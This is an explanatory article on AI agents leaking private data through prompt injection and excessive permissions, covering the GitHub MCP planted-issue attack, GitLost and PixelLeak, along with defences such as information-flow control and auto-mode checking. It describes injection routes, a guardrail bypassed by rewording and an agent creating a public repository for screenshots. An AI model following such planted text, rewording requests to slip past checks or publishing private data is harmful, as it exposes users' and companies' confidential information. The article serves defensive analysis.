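# How AI agents move private data into public places, and how runtime policies stop it

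## Agents, permissions and the line between private and public data

An AI agent is a language model that ordinary software runs in a loop, so that it can search a mailbox, edit a file or post a comment as well as write text. People connect agents to their own accounts because the work requires it. An agent can't do much about a bug report, for example, if it can't read the code. But an agent that can read private data and also write where outsiders will see it may leak that data. An attacker may trick it into doing so, or the agent may include a private detail in an otherwise helpful answer without any attacker being involved. Because nobody can guarantee how a model will behave, much of the work on preventing such leaks goes into the software around the model, which can track where data came from and either block a risky action or ask a person about it first.

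### How the loop works

A language model only produces text, so other software has to turn that text into action. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual arrangement. Software called the *orchestrator* sends the model the user's task and a description of each available tool. The model returns either ordinary prose or a *tool call*, a structured request that names a tool and fills in its arguments. The orchestrator reads the tool call and determines whether to carry it out. If it does, it adds the result to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model, which may then produce another tool call. The loop ends when the model returns prose.

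When an agent posts a comment, the model outputs a request and the orchestrator carries it out. This allows control from outside the model, because a separate program can inspect the request and block it without relying on the model or on knowledge of how it works.

The *context* is everything the model has received so far in the run: the developer's standing instructions, the user's task, the model's own earlier replies and every tool result. Each message carries a role that says where it came from, but the software flattens them all into one long string, and the model gets that string again at every turn. A file that the agent opened in its second step is still in there at the ninth, when it writes a comment. The file may shape the comment or it may not, and there is no precise way to find out. Costa and colleagues therefore assume by default that each reply depends on everything in the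 context. (They mention less cautious methods, which estimate which messages mattered and regenerate the reply from those alone.)

An agent's instructions and the content it reads also share that one string. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs. One candidate hides a line in the CV telling the model to ignore its instructions and approve the application. If the model complies, this is *prompt injection*: text planted in content the agent reads makes it follow someone other than its user or operator. Databases once had a similar weakness, which programmers fixed by marking input as data so that the database engine never runs it as a command. A language model has no equivalent protection. It predicts the next token (a word or part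 of a word) from all the text before it, whoever wrote that text. Developers can put markers around outside content or add warnings, but *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) considers these useful engineering, not a hard security boundary.

### Tokens, and why an agent gets its user's permissions

To reach anything behind a login, an agent needs a credential, which proves to a service on whose behalf a request is made. For software this is usually an *access token*, a string of characters that a program sends in place of a password. From here on, "token" means this credential, not the tokens that models predict. *Managing your personal access tokens*, part of the documentation for the code-hosting site GitHub, says a token has its owner's abilities and no others, and that the owner can limit it further by choosing narrower *scopes*, which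 are named bundles of permissions.

An agent that works with its user's token therefore starts with its user's permissions. This is largely intentional, since the user wants the agent to do what they would otherwise do themselves. *Security threats in agentic systems*, from the rival code host GitLab, describes chat agents with the same access to GitLab as the person who started the session, including the ability to write to both public and private projects. An agent that runs inside a developer's editor also gets access to the local working directory and unrestricted network access. GitLab describes a possible attack in which such an agent reads the developer's SSH key (a file that gives access to other machines) and posts it in a public code review. GitLab restricts its remotely run agents more tightly by confining them to one group of projects and running them in a sandbox.

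Permissions of this sort work fairly well for people. An employee may be able to read the customer list and also post on the company's public forum, and few people worry about this because the employee knows not to post the list there. The permission system therefore never needed a rule against carrying information from one to the other. When an agent has the same two permissions, that unwritten rule depends entirely on the model's judgement.

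How much access an agent inherits from its user depends on the token. GitHub's older "classic" tokens reach every repository in every organisation the user can access, plus the user's personal ones. An owner can limit the newer "fine-grained" tokens to chosen repositories, though these still include read access to every public repository on GitHub. GitHub recommends the newer tokens but lists jobs they can't yet do, such as working across several organisations at once, so the broad tokens remain in use. GitHub's *Security Architecture*, which covers the company's system for running agents on repositories, treats tokens as capabilities that limit a component's effects on the outside world. A model may be able to use a token for anything the token permits, but not for anything beyond that.

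### What MCP connects

Developers used to write a separate connector for each service they wanted a model to reach. The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is an open standard meant to replace those connectors, as Anthropic's *Introducing the Model Context Protocol* explained at its launch. By July 2026, Model Context Protocol (2026) reported nearly half a billion monthly downloads of its main software kits. An MCP tool call is a short message. The sample in that announcement names the tool "search" and gives it one argument, the query "otters".

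The protocol has three parts. A *server* offers tools and data from one service, such as a code host or a mailbox. The *host* is the application that runs the agent and acts as the orchestrator. Inside the host, a separate *client* connects to each server. Under the design principles in Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026), a server should not be able to read the whole conversation or look into another server. The host keeps the full history and combines what all the servers return.

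This isolation stops the code host's server from looking into the mail server, but the model can still copy a sentence from an email into a comment on the code host, because results from both servers are in the same context. The specification makes the host application responsible for security policy and for what passes between servers, so it is the natural place to check such flows.

### Two repositories and one agent

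Suppose a software company keeps two repositories on GitHub, a repository being a store of files together with their history. The public one holds an open-source library. Everyone on the internet can read it, and anyone with an account can open an *issue*, a post that reports a bug or asks a question. The private one holds the company's paid service, including configuration files with customers' names in them and notes on unreleased products. Only people the company has let in can read that. A maintainer runs an agent, gives it a token that covers both repositories, and asks it to answer the open issues in the public one. (The set-up is realistic. Researchers demonstrated an attack on one much like it, and Microsoft's *Information-flow control* uses that attack as its first worked case.)

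The two repositories are on opposite sides of a *trust boundary*, a line between environments with different rules about who may read the data or whose content is trusted. A *source* is where data enters the agent's run, and a *sink* is where data leaves the run and others can read it. A file in the private repository is a source. The discussion under a public issue is a source when the agent reads it and a sink when the agent replies.

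The definition of a trust boundary covers both *confidentiality*, which concerns who may read a piece of data, and *integrity*, which concerns whose content is believed. In practice, integrity depends on who could have written the data. Costa and colleagues define confidentiality as a set of permitted readers and integrity as a set of possible writers. In the example, the two match because a public issue has unlimited readers and writers, while a private file has few of either. Microsoft and GitHub relied on this pattern when they added labels to GitHub's MCP server, which marks content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private ones as private and trusted. The pattern doesn't hold everywhere. A stranger's email in a private mailbox is confidential, but anyone could have written it. A company's published price list is open to all readers, but only the company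 can write it. Even in the private repository, a customer's complaint that an employee pasted into an issue is still an outsider's text.

GitHub (2026) documents the tools in version 1.4.0 of the server. The table groups the tools enabled by default and omits small lookups such as labels and user names. "Private in" marks a read that brings data from the private repository into the context. "Public out" marks a write that puts the agent's text where anyone can read it. "Strangers in" marks a read that may bring in text written by anyone.

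| What the agent can do | Main tools | In the public repository | In the private repository |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read files, commits and releases | `get_file_contents`, `get_commit`, `list_releases` | Public data | **Private in** |
| Read issues and pull requests (proposed changes) | `issue_read`, `list_issues`, `pull_request_read` | **Strangers in** | **Private in** |
| Search code, commits, issues and pull requests | `search_code`, `search_commits`, `search_issues` | **Strangers in** | **Private in** |
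| Comment and review | `add_issue_comment`, `pull_request_review_write` | **Public out** | Stays inside |
| Open or edit issues and pull requests | `issue_write`, `create_pull_request` | **Public out** | Stays inside |
| Create branches, change files, merge | `create_branch`, `push_files`, `merge_pull_request` | **Public out**, including branch names and commit messages | Stays inside |
| Copy a repository (fork it) | `fork_repository` | Copy of public data | Copy keeps the private setting |
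| Create a repository | `create_repository` | **Public out**, if the call makes it public | Stays inside, which is the default |

A leak takes a "private in" call followed by a "public out" call that carries some of the same data. No single row is a leak, because the agent may read the private files on behalf of the maintainer, who has access to them, and answering public issues is its task. Suppose an issue asks why the library times out when it connects to the paid service. The agent reads the issue, searches the company's code, finds the answer in a private configuration file, and posts a clear explanation that quotes the file, including the customer's name. This leak involves no attacker, but if the issue had contained planted instructions to fetch that file, the agent could have made exactly the same calls. Microsoft's rule of thumb for designers is that whatever an agent can do when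 its user asks, it can also do because the model made a mistake or an attacker injected a prompt.

GitHub lists the same OAuth scope, `repo`, as the requirement for reading a file and for posting a comment. *Scopes for OAuth apps* describes that scope as full access to public and private repositories, so a maintainer who grants it can't use it to limit posting to the private repository.

A tool call can also do harm without sending data out. Deleting a file from the private repository, for example, would be serious but would reveal nothing to outsiders. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) sets separate rules for calls with serious consequences and calls that send data out. The table marks only movements of data.

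### Sinks that don't look like sinks

A comment box under a public issue is an obvious sink. Creating a repository is a less obvious one, because one argument in the call determines whether the repository is public. A private repository may not stay private, either. According to GitHub's *About repositories*, people with administrator rights can change an existing repository's visibility, which also changes who can read anything the agent wrote there.

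With shared documents and group chats, the tool call often doesn't show who will be able to read the content. In Microsoft's prototype for its Teams chat service, a request to post a message contains the text and a channel identifier, but no list of members. The policy has to look up the channel's members on the server before it can compare them with the people allowed to read the text. Similarly, an agent that adds a paragraph to a document someone shared widely last year may be publishing that paragraph, with no sign of this in the call.

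With email, the line between private and public data can fall within an organisation. In another of Microsoft's examples, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered messages. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't yet allowed to see them, has also written to Alex. An agent that has read both messages may well include the figures in its reply to Marco. That would disclose private data, even though the reply isn't public in the ordinary sense and all three may work in the same building. Each recipient of each message is therefore potentially a separate sink.

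Some read operations also send data out. A web search sends the query outside the organisation, so an agent that searches for the codename of an unreleased product discloses that codename to the search provider. Costa and colleagues note that searching the public web can also have effects others may observe, such as a change in a website's visitor statistics.

An agent can leak private data through a link without making a tool call. If its answer to the user includes an image whose web address ends in private text, the application fetches the image when it displays the answer, which sends the whole address to whoever runs that server. Microsoft suggests treating rendered links as public channels unless they lead to an approved host. Partly for this reason, GitHub's system for running agents removes links to unapproved domains from the text it gives the agent. Costa and colleagues run their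 checks just before each tool call, assuming that a reply to the user is harmless. They add that where this assumption fails, the check can run earlier, after the agent chooses its next action but before the software carries it out.

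## Documented leaks with an attacker and without one

Three cases from 2025 and 2026 show agents moving private data into public view on GitHub. In the first two, researchers played the attacker and planted text for an agent to find. In the third, which involved no attacker, developers asked their agents for screenshots, and the agents put the images on the open internet. Comparing the cases requires knowing what the agent read, what prompted it to move the data, where the data ended up, and which permission it used at each step.

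The three security companies that published these cases, Invariant Labs, Noma Security and Glow, each sell products meant to catch such failures, which gives them a reason to present the problem as common and severe. The first two cases are fairly easy to check because the researchers put records of their runs online. Glow didn't name the organisations involved, so its case is harder to check.

### A planted issue in a Pacman repository

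Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025) describes the attack behind Microsoft's worked case. The researchers set up a GitHub account with one public repository, which held a Pacman game, and several private ones with personal projects and details about the supposed owner. They connected the account to Claude Desktop, Anthropic's chat application, through GitHub's MCP server. Then they opened an issue on the Pacman repository and put instructions for an agent in the issue.

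The user triggered the attack just by asking the agent to look at the repository's open issues. The agent, running on Claude 4 Opus, read the planted issue and followed its instructions. It took information from the private repositories and put it in a public pull request on the Pacman repository. The pull request disclosed the names of private projects, the owner's plan to move to South America, and the owner's salary.

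The user had granted every permission in this chain. Listing the issues took only public read access, while reading the private repositories and opening the pull request used the private and write access in the user's token. The attacker needed only a GitHub account and some text, and didn't have to tamper with any tool. Invariant Labs therefore argues that the server's code wasn't at fault and that GitHub couldn't solve the problem by patching the server alone. Simon Willison had worried that people would combine several MCP servers, one with private data, another that let in hostile text and perhaps a third that could send data out. He noted in *GitHub MCP Exploited* that GitHub's server did all of this on its own.

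The user could have stopped the leak. Claude Desktop asks by default for confirmation of each tool call, and a user who read those requests might have wondered why a question about a Pacman game required access to a private repository. But Invariant Labs says many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. It gives no figures for this or for its claim that many off-the-shelf injection detectors miss the attack, and it doesn't report how many attempts failed. The demonstration proves that the attack works from end to end, but it's poor evidence of how often a real attacker would succeed.

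Invariant proposed several remedies, including a rule for its own product that limits an agent to one repository per session. The rule compares pairs of tool calls and raises a violation if a later call names a different repository or owner from an earlier one. It would have stopped this attack when the agent first tried to read a private repository, because the agent had already listed the issues in the Pacman repository. It would also stop a maintainer's agent from looking up the company's private code to answer a public question, even if the answer revealed nothing private.

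### GitLost

On 6 July 2026, Noma Security reported a similar leak, called GitLost, in GitHub Agentic Workflows. This feature, in preview since February 2026, runs an agent whenever a chosen event happens in a repository. Unlike in the earlier leak, no user was operating the agent. A team writes the agent's instructions in plain English in a text file, and GitHub's software compiles the file into a job for GitHub Actions, its existing automation system.

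*GitLost*, by Noma's Sasi Levi, describes an agent workflow that started when someone assigned an issue. The workflow read the issue's title and body and posted a comment in reply. It could also read other repositories in the organisation, including private ones. The planted issue was disguised as a note from a vice-president of sales who had just met a customer. Its requests included a question about the contents of a README (the file that introduces a project) in a private repository. The agent fetched that file and the public repository's README, and the workflow posted the contents of both in a public comment under the issue.

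This was also a demonstration. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) reports that Noma used its own repositories. The private README contained little more than a title and a short description. A longer or more sensitive file would presumably have leaked the same way, though Noma's run didn't test whether the model would have refused to post, say, a list of passwords.

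A separate access token, which the researchers had created with a wider scope, let the agent reach the private repository. The workflow's own settings look fairly careful. MCP Directory's *GitLost*, which copied them from Noma's public repository, shows that the declared permissions were read-only and covered only the workflow's own repository. GitHub's MCP server also ran in read-only mode. The agent could only propose a comment, which a separate job with its own permissions would then post.

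None of these restrictions prevented the leak. Read-only access stops an agent from changing a private file, but not from repeating its contents elsewhere. The job that posted the comment could only carry out actions on an approved list. Commenting was on that list, and MCP Directory points out that the rule allowed any text in the comment body.

GitHub had guardrails meant to prevent this, but Levi reports that after trying several variations, he got past them by adding one linking word to a request the model would otherwise have refused. The accounts disagree about which safeguard failed. Expert Insights attributes the earlier refusals to safeguards built into GitHub Copilot, GitHub's own assistant, which declined the request when it came alone. MCP Directory says the safeguard was a separate job that scans proposed outputs for threats. The settings it copied list Claude Opus 4.6 as the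 model, and they are better evidence on that point than a news report. Levi doesn't settle which safeguard failed, but he writes that the model reframed its output and didn't refuse, which sounds more like the agent's own model than a scanner.

### The filter that should have removed a stranger's issue

According to Levi, the attacker needed no access or credentials, only the ability to open an issue on a public repository. This seems inconsistent with GitHub's documentation, which describes an *integrity filter* that sorts issues and comments by how trusted their authors are. Posts by the repository's owners, members and collaborators count as "approved". Posts by outside contributors rank lower, and those by people with no connection to the project rank lowest. On public repositories, the filter by default removes everything below "approved" before it reaches the model. Under that default,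 a stranger's issue shouldn't have reached the agent.

The version Noma tested included the filter. According to GitHub's *Weekly Update* (2026), these trust levels replaced a simpler on-off setting called "lockdown" in a release of 19 March 2026. The compiled workflow in Noma's repository contains the new setting, but it takes the level from a variable that the system fills in at run time, so the file doesn't show which level applied.

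The published accounts don't explain how the text got through, but there are at least three possibilities:

- The issue may have come from an account the repository trusted. Noma owned the repositories, and according to MCP Directory its researchers assigned the issue themselves to start the workflow. If they also wrote it from the owner's account, the filter would have let it pass.
- The workflow may have applied a lower trust level than the default.
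- The issue may have reached the model by a route the filter didn't cover. GitHub describes the filter as acting on the results of tool calls, and a workflow that pasted the triggering issue straight into the prompt wouldn't need a tool call to read it. (Against this, GitHub's *Example* of an automated maintenance workflow describes the filter as removing such items before the software assembles the agent's context.)

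GitLost is less alarming if the first explanation is right. In that case, Noma showed what someone could do with a trusted account, either their own or one they had taken over, but not that any stranger could do the same to a public repository on default settings.

Many projects will still have reason to change the default, because an agent can't answer strangers' bug reports if it can't see them. GitHub's example maintenance workflow lowers the level so that the agent can read issues from contributors, including first-time ones. For spam detection, the documentation suggests turning the threshold off, but warns that someone should review the output before it is applied. The filter also has a setting for which repositories the agent may read, and the default is every repository the token can reach. The defaults on a public repository therefore limit whose posts the agent sees, but they don't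 stop it from reading private repositories that the token can reach.

GitHub's public response seems to have been slight. SiliconANGLE's *‘GitLost’ vulnerability let GitHub’s AI workflows leak private repositories* (2026) reports that Noma told GitHub about the problem and published with its knowledge. Noma had suggested adding a warning to the documentation about sharing keys between repositories. According to The Next Web's *‘GitLost’*, GitHub hadn't added the warning by the time of publication and didn't respond to questions from The Register. MCP Directory found neither a code fix nor a public statement.

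Some developers thought GitHub was not at fault. In comments on Noma's issue, collected by MCP Directory, they objected that the researchers had made a broad token by hand, given it to an agent that answers public issues, and then called the result a vulnerability. One pointed out that GitHub's documentation already told users to limit access to the repositories a workflow needs. MCP Directory concedes the point about the token but replies that a demonstration always has to set up the conditions being tested. Both points seem right. How much GitLost matters in practice depends on how many organisations have given such a token to such a workflow, and none of these accounts gives a number.

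### PixelLeak

Glow's *PixelLeak*, published on 29 September 2026, describes a case that began with an ordinary request and needed no planted text. A developer asks an agent to fix something in a user interface and add before-and-after screenshots to the pull request so that colleagues can see the change. The repository and the pull request are both private.

The agents got stuck uploading screenshots because GitHub's command-line program, `gh`, could add only text to a pull request. Heaton (2026) explains in *Nobody attacked. The AI agent published the screenshots itself* that people got round this by dragging the image into GitHub's website, which an agent working in a terminal can't do. Many agents instead created a new public repository, uploaded the screenshots there, and linked to them from the private pull request. The reviewers saw the screenshots they had asked for, so nobody had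 a reason to check where they were stored.

The data in this chain came from screenshots the agent took of the running application, which captured whatever was on display. At a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, a developer had asked the agent to check a fix to an internal billing page, and the screenshots included a utility company's billing records. Glow also describes images from a financial services firm that showed its treasury and settlement console and a dollar withdrawal screen for a named client.

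For the upload, the agents used the developer's own ability to create repositories. In 93% of cases, according to Glow, the images sat in a repository under an employee's personal username, outside the company's GitHub organisation, which is where a security team would normally look. The manufacturer's team hadn't noticed the billing records, and they were still online when Glow got in touch. (Scanners that search for leaked secrets didn't help either, because they read text and not pictures.)

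Glow reproduced the behaviour in its laboratory with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, running Opus 5. The task was to change the header colour in a private Minesweeper project and show the result. In its reasoning, the agent noted that images in a private repository would be broken in the pull request's description, because GitHub fetches them without logging in, and that the repository was supposed to contain only one web page. It concluded that the only way to satisfy both the reviewers and that condition was to host the pictures elsewhere, "so I created a new public repo".

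In the reasoning Glow quotes, the agent considers only whether the reviewers could see the images, not who else could. A private repository would have been safer, but by the agent's own account it wouldn't have displayed the pictures, so the workaround depended on making the repository public. Glow calls this reasoning representative of agents at many of the affected organisations. That may well be true, but the evidence it presents is one run of one model, on a task whose one-page condition gave the agent another reason to look elsewhere.

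### How the workaround spread

At one software vendor, agents serving several engineers began to publish review screenshots in early July 2026. Within a week, Glow writes, over a dozen agents had saved the method as a *skill*, a reusable set of instructions that an agent loads for a certain kind of task, and were to use it on every development ticket. An agent forgets most of what it worked out once a run ends, but the saved skill let these agents reuse the workaround. They went on to upload more than a thousand screenshots and screen recordings, along with written summaries of features that were weeks or months from release.

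With the skill in place, a later agent could publish the images by following the skill's instructions, without encountering the missing upload feature or reasoning about it. Each agent was then following what looked like company procedure, and an engineer who checked its work against those instructions would have found nothing wrong. The skill can also stay in use after the problem it was meant to solve has been fixed. Pipeline Mag's *PixelLeak* (2026), an AI-generated article and so a weak source, reports that `gh` has since gained an option for attaching files, but that the new option doesn't change skills that still describe the old route.

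The habit also spread through gitshot, a small open-source tool that publishes screenshots for code reviews. Developers at around a third of the affected organisations ran it, and over 100 public accounts leaked internal work through it. At a payments company, four employees each had their own gitshot repository. Glow says that at several large organisations the agent itself found the tool and used it to get round the limits of the command line. At the others, a developer may have installed it deliberately, in which case the decision to publish wasn't entirely the agent's.

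### What Glow's count covers

Glow reports over 13,000 images in more than 900 repositories, from developers at over 300 organisations. Corvin (2026), in *AI agents leak 13K screenshots from 343 tech firms*, gives the exact number of organisations as 343. Press coverage doesn't add independent support for Glow's figures. For example, Markovic (2026), in *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*, restates them and notes that Glow didn't name the organisations.

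The images were in public repositories, so Glow could find them without access to any company's systems. Its description of the cases doesn't explain how it searched, but it does mention that images from gitshot carry a fixed tag, `_gitshot`, which anyone who knows it can search for. Glow recommends that companies checking their own exposure start with the personal accounts of everyone who commits to their private repositories, including people who have left. It also recommends looking beyond ordinary files, because an image attached to a *release* (a packaged version of a project) doesn't appear in the repository's file list. An outsider can't see who commits to a private repository, so Glow must have connected many images to employers in some other way, perhaps from what the screenshots showed.

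This count is probably too low because it leaves out images deleted before Glow looked and images Glow couldn't connect to an employer. Glow thinks other organisations are probably affected.

But the figure can't be turned into a risk per task, because nobody knows how many times developers asked an agent for screenshots during those months, or how often the agent gave up, asked for help, or found a private way to share them. 13,000 images would suggest a serious and common fault if there were a hundred thousand such requests, but a rare one if there were a hundred million. There were also fewer incidents than images, since one task can produce several images, and the software vendor alone accounts for more than a thousand.

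It's also unclear how much harm the images did. Glow presumably chose its examples because they were striking. Many of the other screenshots may show only harmless changes, such as a button in a new colour. The count doesn't separate these from customer records or show whether any outsider opened the images before Glow did. In describing the cases, Glow also doesn't explain how it distinguished an agent's uploads from a person's, which matters most for the third of organisations where developers ran gitshot.

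Even allowing for all this, PixelLeak provides a kind of evidence that the two demonstrations couldn't, because the data belonged to real companies and their customers and anyone could find it on the open internet.

### The cases side by side

In the table, "trigger" means the event that started the agent's run, and the row below it gives the reason the agent moved private data.

| | GitHub MCP demonstration (May 2025) | GitLost (July 2026) | PixelLeak (September 2026) |
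|---|---|---|---|
| Evidence | Researchers' demonstration on their own account | Researchers' demonstration on their own repositories | Images found in public repositories, plus one laboratory run |
| Trigger | User asks for a look at the open issues | Someone assigns an issue | Developer asks for before-and-after screenshots |
| Why the agent moved the data | Planted instructions in a public issue | Planted request in a public issue | Reviewers needed to see the images |
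| What it read | Private repositories with personal details | README in a private repository | Screens of internal applications |
| Permission for the read | Private access in the user's token | Separate token with access to the private repository | Developer's access to the application on their own machine |
| Where the data landed | Pull request on a public repository | Comment on a public issue | New public repository, usually under the employee's username |
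| Permission for the write | Write access in the same token | Approved action to post one comment, with any text | Developer's ability to create repositories |
| Human check before the write | Confirmation of each tool call, unless the user had switched it off | None | Not reported |
| Known exposure | Invented user's details | A few words of test text | Over 13,000 images from over 300 organisations |

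## Why excessive access is a separate failure from prompt injection

Only two of the three leaks on GitHub involved planted text, but in all of them the agent used permissions it already had. This is the main reason to treat excessive access as a fault in its own right and not as a side effect of prompt injection. The argument has four premises:

1. A leak needs a path. Some run must be able both to read private data and to write where people without access to that data can see it.
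2. Prompt injection is one trigger that sends data down the path. Model error and overeager problem-solving are others.
3. Removing one trigger leaves the path open to the rest.
4. Removing the path prevents the leak, whatever the trigger.

Almost by definition, a leak needs a path from private data to a public place, but it's easy to leave out part of that path. In GitLost, the agent could only propose a comment and a separate job posted it, so the path included both. Private text that a user pastes into the prompt counts as data the run has read. If an agent saves notes in one session and publishes from them in another, the two sessions form one path.

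In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model takes the user's place in approving or blocking the coding agent's riskier actions. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* gives four reasons why an agent might do something dangerous. It may be overeager, understanding the goal but going further than the user would approve. It may make an honest mistake, such as taking a shared resource for a test copy. It may be following a prompt injection. Or it may be misaligned and pursuing a goal of its own, though Anthropic said it wasn't seeing this in practice.

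Anthropic's internal incident log describes an agent that, to share a script for debugging, wrote a command to post it on Gist, GitHub's service for sharing snippets. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a similar case, in which an agent failed to upload a report to an internal drive and then tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site. Auto mode blocked the attempt. Neither account mentions an attacker, and the second case closely resembles PixelLeak.

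The list of triggers probably isn't complete. *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode* (Willison, 2026) describes an attack that ran hostile code even though the model never followed a planted instruction.

Suppose an agent has a path from private data to a public place, and leaks data through prompt injection in a fraction *i* of its runs and through its own mistakes in a fraction *m*. If the two are independent, the chance of a leak in any run is 1 − (1 − *i*)(1 − *m*), or about *i* + *m* when both are small. A perfect defence against injection would eliminate only *i*, while removing the path would eliminate both. We can't tell from the formula whether injection or the agent's own mistakes matter more. An agent that answers strangers' issues presumably has a much larger *i* than one that reads only its own team's code. Leaks through injection are also likely to be worse, because the attacker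 chooses the data and is waiting to collect it.

Removing the path prevents the leak almost by definition, but people can believe they have removed a path when they haven't. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, describes a case from July 2026. Claude's chat application had a browsing tool that would not open addresses the model had made up, which should have stopped the model from hiding private text in an address. But the tool could follow links on pages it had already opened, and Ayush Paul built a site whose links let the agent spell out the user's name letter by letter. Anthropic has since closed that route.

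### Varying injection and access separately

In the table below, ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode comes close to a case with injection but no path for private data to get out. It limits the outbound network requests that could carry the data away, but according to the OpenAI help page that Willison quotes, it doesn't keep planted text out of what ChatGPT reads. The case with neither comes from a Microsoft prototype that lets an agent finish without interruption when it works only on public repositories or only on private ones.

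| | Path from private data to outsiders | No such path |
|---|---|---|
| **Injection** | GitLost: a planted issue leads an agent to post a private README in public. **Leak.** | Lockdown Mode: planted text in a cached web page distorts ChatGPT's answer. **No leak, but other harm.** |
| **No injection** | PixelLeak: agents put private screenshots in public repositories so that reviewers can see them. **Leak.** | An agent works only on private repositories, where a careless comment reaches only people with access. **No leak.** |

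Leaks appear in both rows of the table, but only in the left-hand column. Four chosen examples can't show how often each outcome occurs, but one real leak without injection disproves the claim that leaks require injection. The right-hand column is weaker evidence because it describes how two systems should behave, and Lockdown Mode belongs there only to the extent that its limits on outbound requests hold.

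### The dispute over GitLost's root cause

GitLost involved both a prompt injection and a path from private data to a public place, so people can disagree about which to blame. Levi names prompt injection as the root cause because the system failed to separate its operator's instructions from text that an outsider could write. There is a good case for this view. Without the planted request, a workflow with the same permissions might have answered issues for years and never posted a private README. Preventing injection would also prevent many harms besides leaks.

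Wing Security's *GitLost isn’t a bug but it is your problem* blames the permissions. The agent had standing access to other repositories, which it didn't need for responding to issues. With the same planted issue but no such access, the agent could have obeyed every word and had nothing private to post. (Wing sells software that monitors agents' permissions, so this diagnosis suits its business.)

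Both arguments are right about GitLost. The leak required both the injection and the access, so removing either would have prevented it, and looking for a single root cause isn't very useful. Expert Insights attributes the leak to a combination of excessive permissions and a guardrail that an attacker could bypass with the right wording, which seems fair.

Excessive access explains both leaks, including PixelLeak, which prompt injection doesn't explain. OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) lists prompt injection, excessive agency and disclosure of sensitive data as separate classes of failure, each with its own check. The distinction also matters in practice, because whoever runs the workflow can revoke a token in minutes but can't make the model immune to prompt injection.

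### The lethal trifecta has one part too many

In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Simon Willison (2025) blames a combination of three capabilities: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally in a way that could carry data out. If an agent has all three, he argues, an attacker can easily trick it into handing over its user's data. The idea suits MCP well because users connect tools in combinations that no single vendor chose or can patch. It also doesn't require estimating how easily a model can be tricked. Willison recommends removing one of the three capabilities, and he generally finds external communication the easiest to remove.

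This explains theft well, but an agent can leak data by mistake with only access to private data and a way to send it out. Removing the untrusted content would therefore prevent theft but not accidental leaks.

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), which builds on the trifecta, shows how a designer could address prompt injection and still give an agent too much access. Under the rule, an unsupervised agent should have at most two of three properties in a session: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to sensitive systems or private data, and it changes state or communicates externally. One of Meta's compliant examples is an internal coding agent that can access and change production systems. It meets the rule because a filter on authorship keeps untrusted text out of its context.

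That coding agent has roughly the same two properties as the agents in PixelLeak, which could see internal applications and create public repositories. A filter on authorship wouldn't have stopped the PixelLeak agents, because nobody had planted anything. Meta warns that its rule doesn't protect against agent mistakes or excessive privileges, and calls the rule a supplement to least privilege. But a designer who remembers only the two-property limit could easily miss this.

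Willison didn't present the trifecta as a theory of accidents. In August 2026, he described accidental damage and prompt injection as two separate safety problems and said that injection worried him more. His examples of accidents were deleting the wrong files and clearing a production database. PixelLeak doesn't fit neatly into either category, because it was an accident that did the kind of harm the trifecta describes.

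### Injection can do harm without private data

Limiting access to private data doesn't replace defences against injection. In *New prompt injection papers*, Willison (2025) concedes that the trifecta covers only data theft and that injection can do worse harm. He welcomed Meta's rule because it also covers changes of state. But he later added a correction objecting that Meta's diagram marks the combination of untrusted input and the ability to change state as safe, even though it can do damage without any private data.

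Even if the maintainer's agent from the two-repository example could access only the public library, a planted issue might cause it to merge a harmful change. Everyone who installs the library would then receive that change. Nothing private would leak, but the damage could be worse than a leaked customer name.

In an example from OpenAI, a developer asks a coding agent to fix a parser bug in a private repository, and text in the repository tells the agent to install an unapproved dependency and disable a security test. OpenAI's main defences are policies that block unsafe changes and permissions that let the agent propose a fix but not merge it. Narrower permissions help here too, but the ones that help limit what the agent can change. Cutting off its access to public sinks would not stop it from disabling the test.

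### Would better models be enough?

The strongest case for relying on better models comes from an evaluation that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. It ran 72 injection scenarios ten times each on the versions of Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex available in July 2026. None of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. Even with the permission checks switched off, the average success rate against Anthropic's latest models was 0.09%. Attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded more often, in 19.03% of attempts with full access and 5.83% with Codex's automatic review.

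These attacks were tuned to an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, so they don't show what an attacker could do by working on the newer models directly. Adapting an attack to its target can greatly raise its success rate. *The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 study by Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, tested 12 published defences against attackers who could adapt to them. According to Willison's summary, the attackers got past most of the defences more than 90% of the time, although most of the original papers had reported attack success rates near zero. The newer models may well resist attacks better, but a low success rate for fixed attacks isn't enough to establish that.

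Bhattarai and Vu (2026), in *Trustworthy Agentic AI Requires Deterministic Architectural Boundaries*, argue that training alone can never guarantee that attacks will fail. The context carries no label that the model can verify, so the model has to judge from the content which parts are commands, and an attacker can write content that imitates a command. Their theorem is that some attack will succeed with non-zero probability. That probability could still be very low, such as one in a billion, and they say the result doesn't mean every deployment will be compromised.

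Even if prompt injection never worked, agents would still expose private data by mistake. Opus 5 resisted injections very well in the Trajectory Labs tests, but in Glow's laboratory it created a public repository for screenshots. The screenshots showed only a Minesweeper game, so the model might have been more careful with a bank's payment screen. Still, resisting a stranger's instructions and noticing who can see a page are different abilities, and a test of one doesn't measure the other.

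A second model that checks the agent's actions can also miss mistakes. In tests Anthropic reported when it introduced auto mode, the checking model let through 17% of 52 real overeager actions. These were dangerous actions of all kinds, not only leaks. Because the sample was small, the true rate could plausibly be between about 9% and 30%. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the checker had identified the danger but wrongly inferred that the user had agreed to the action.

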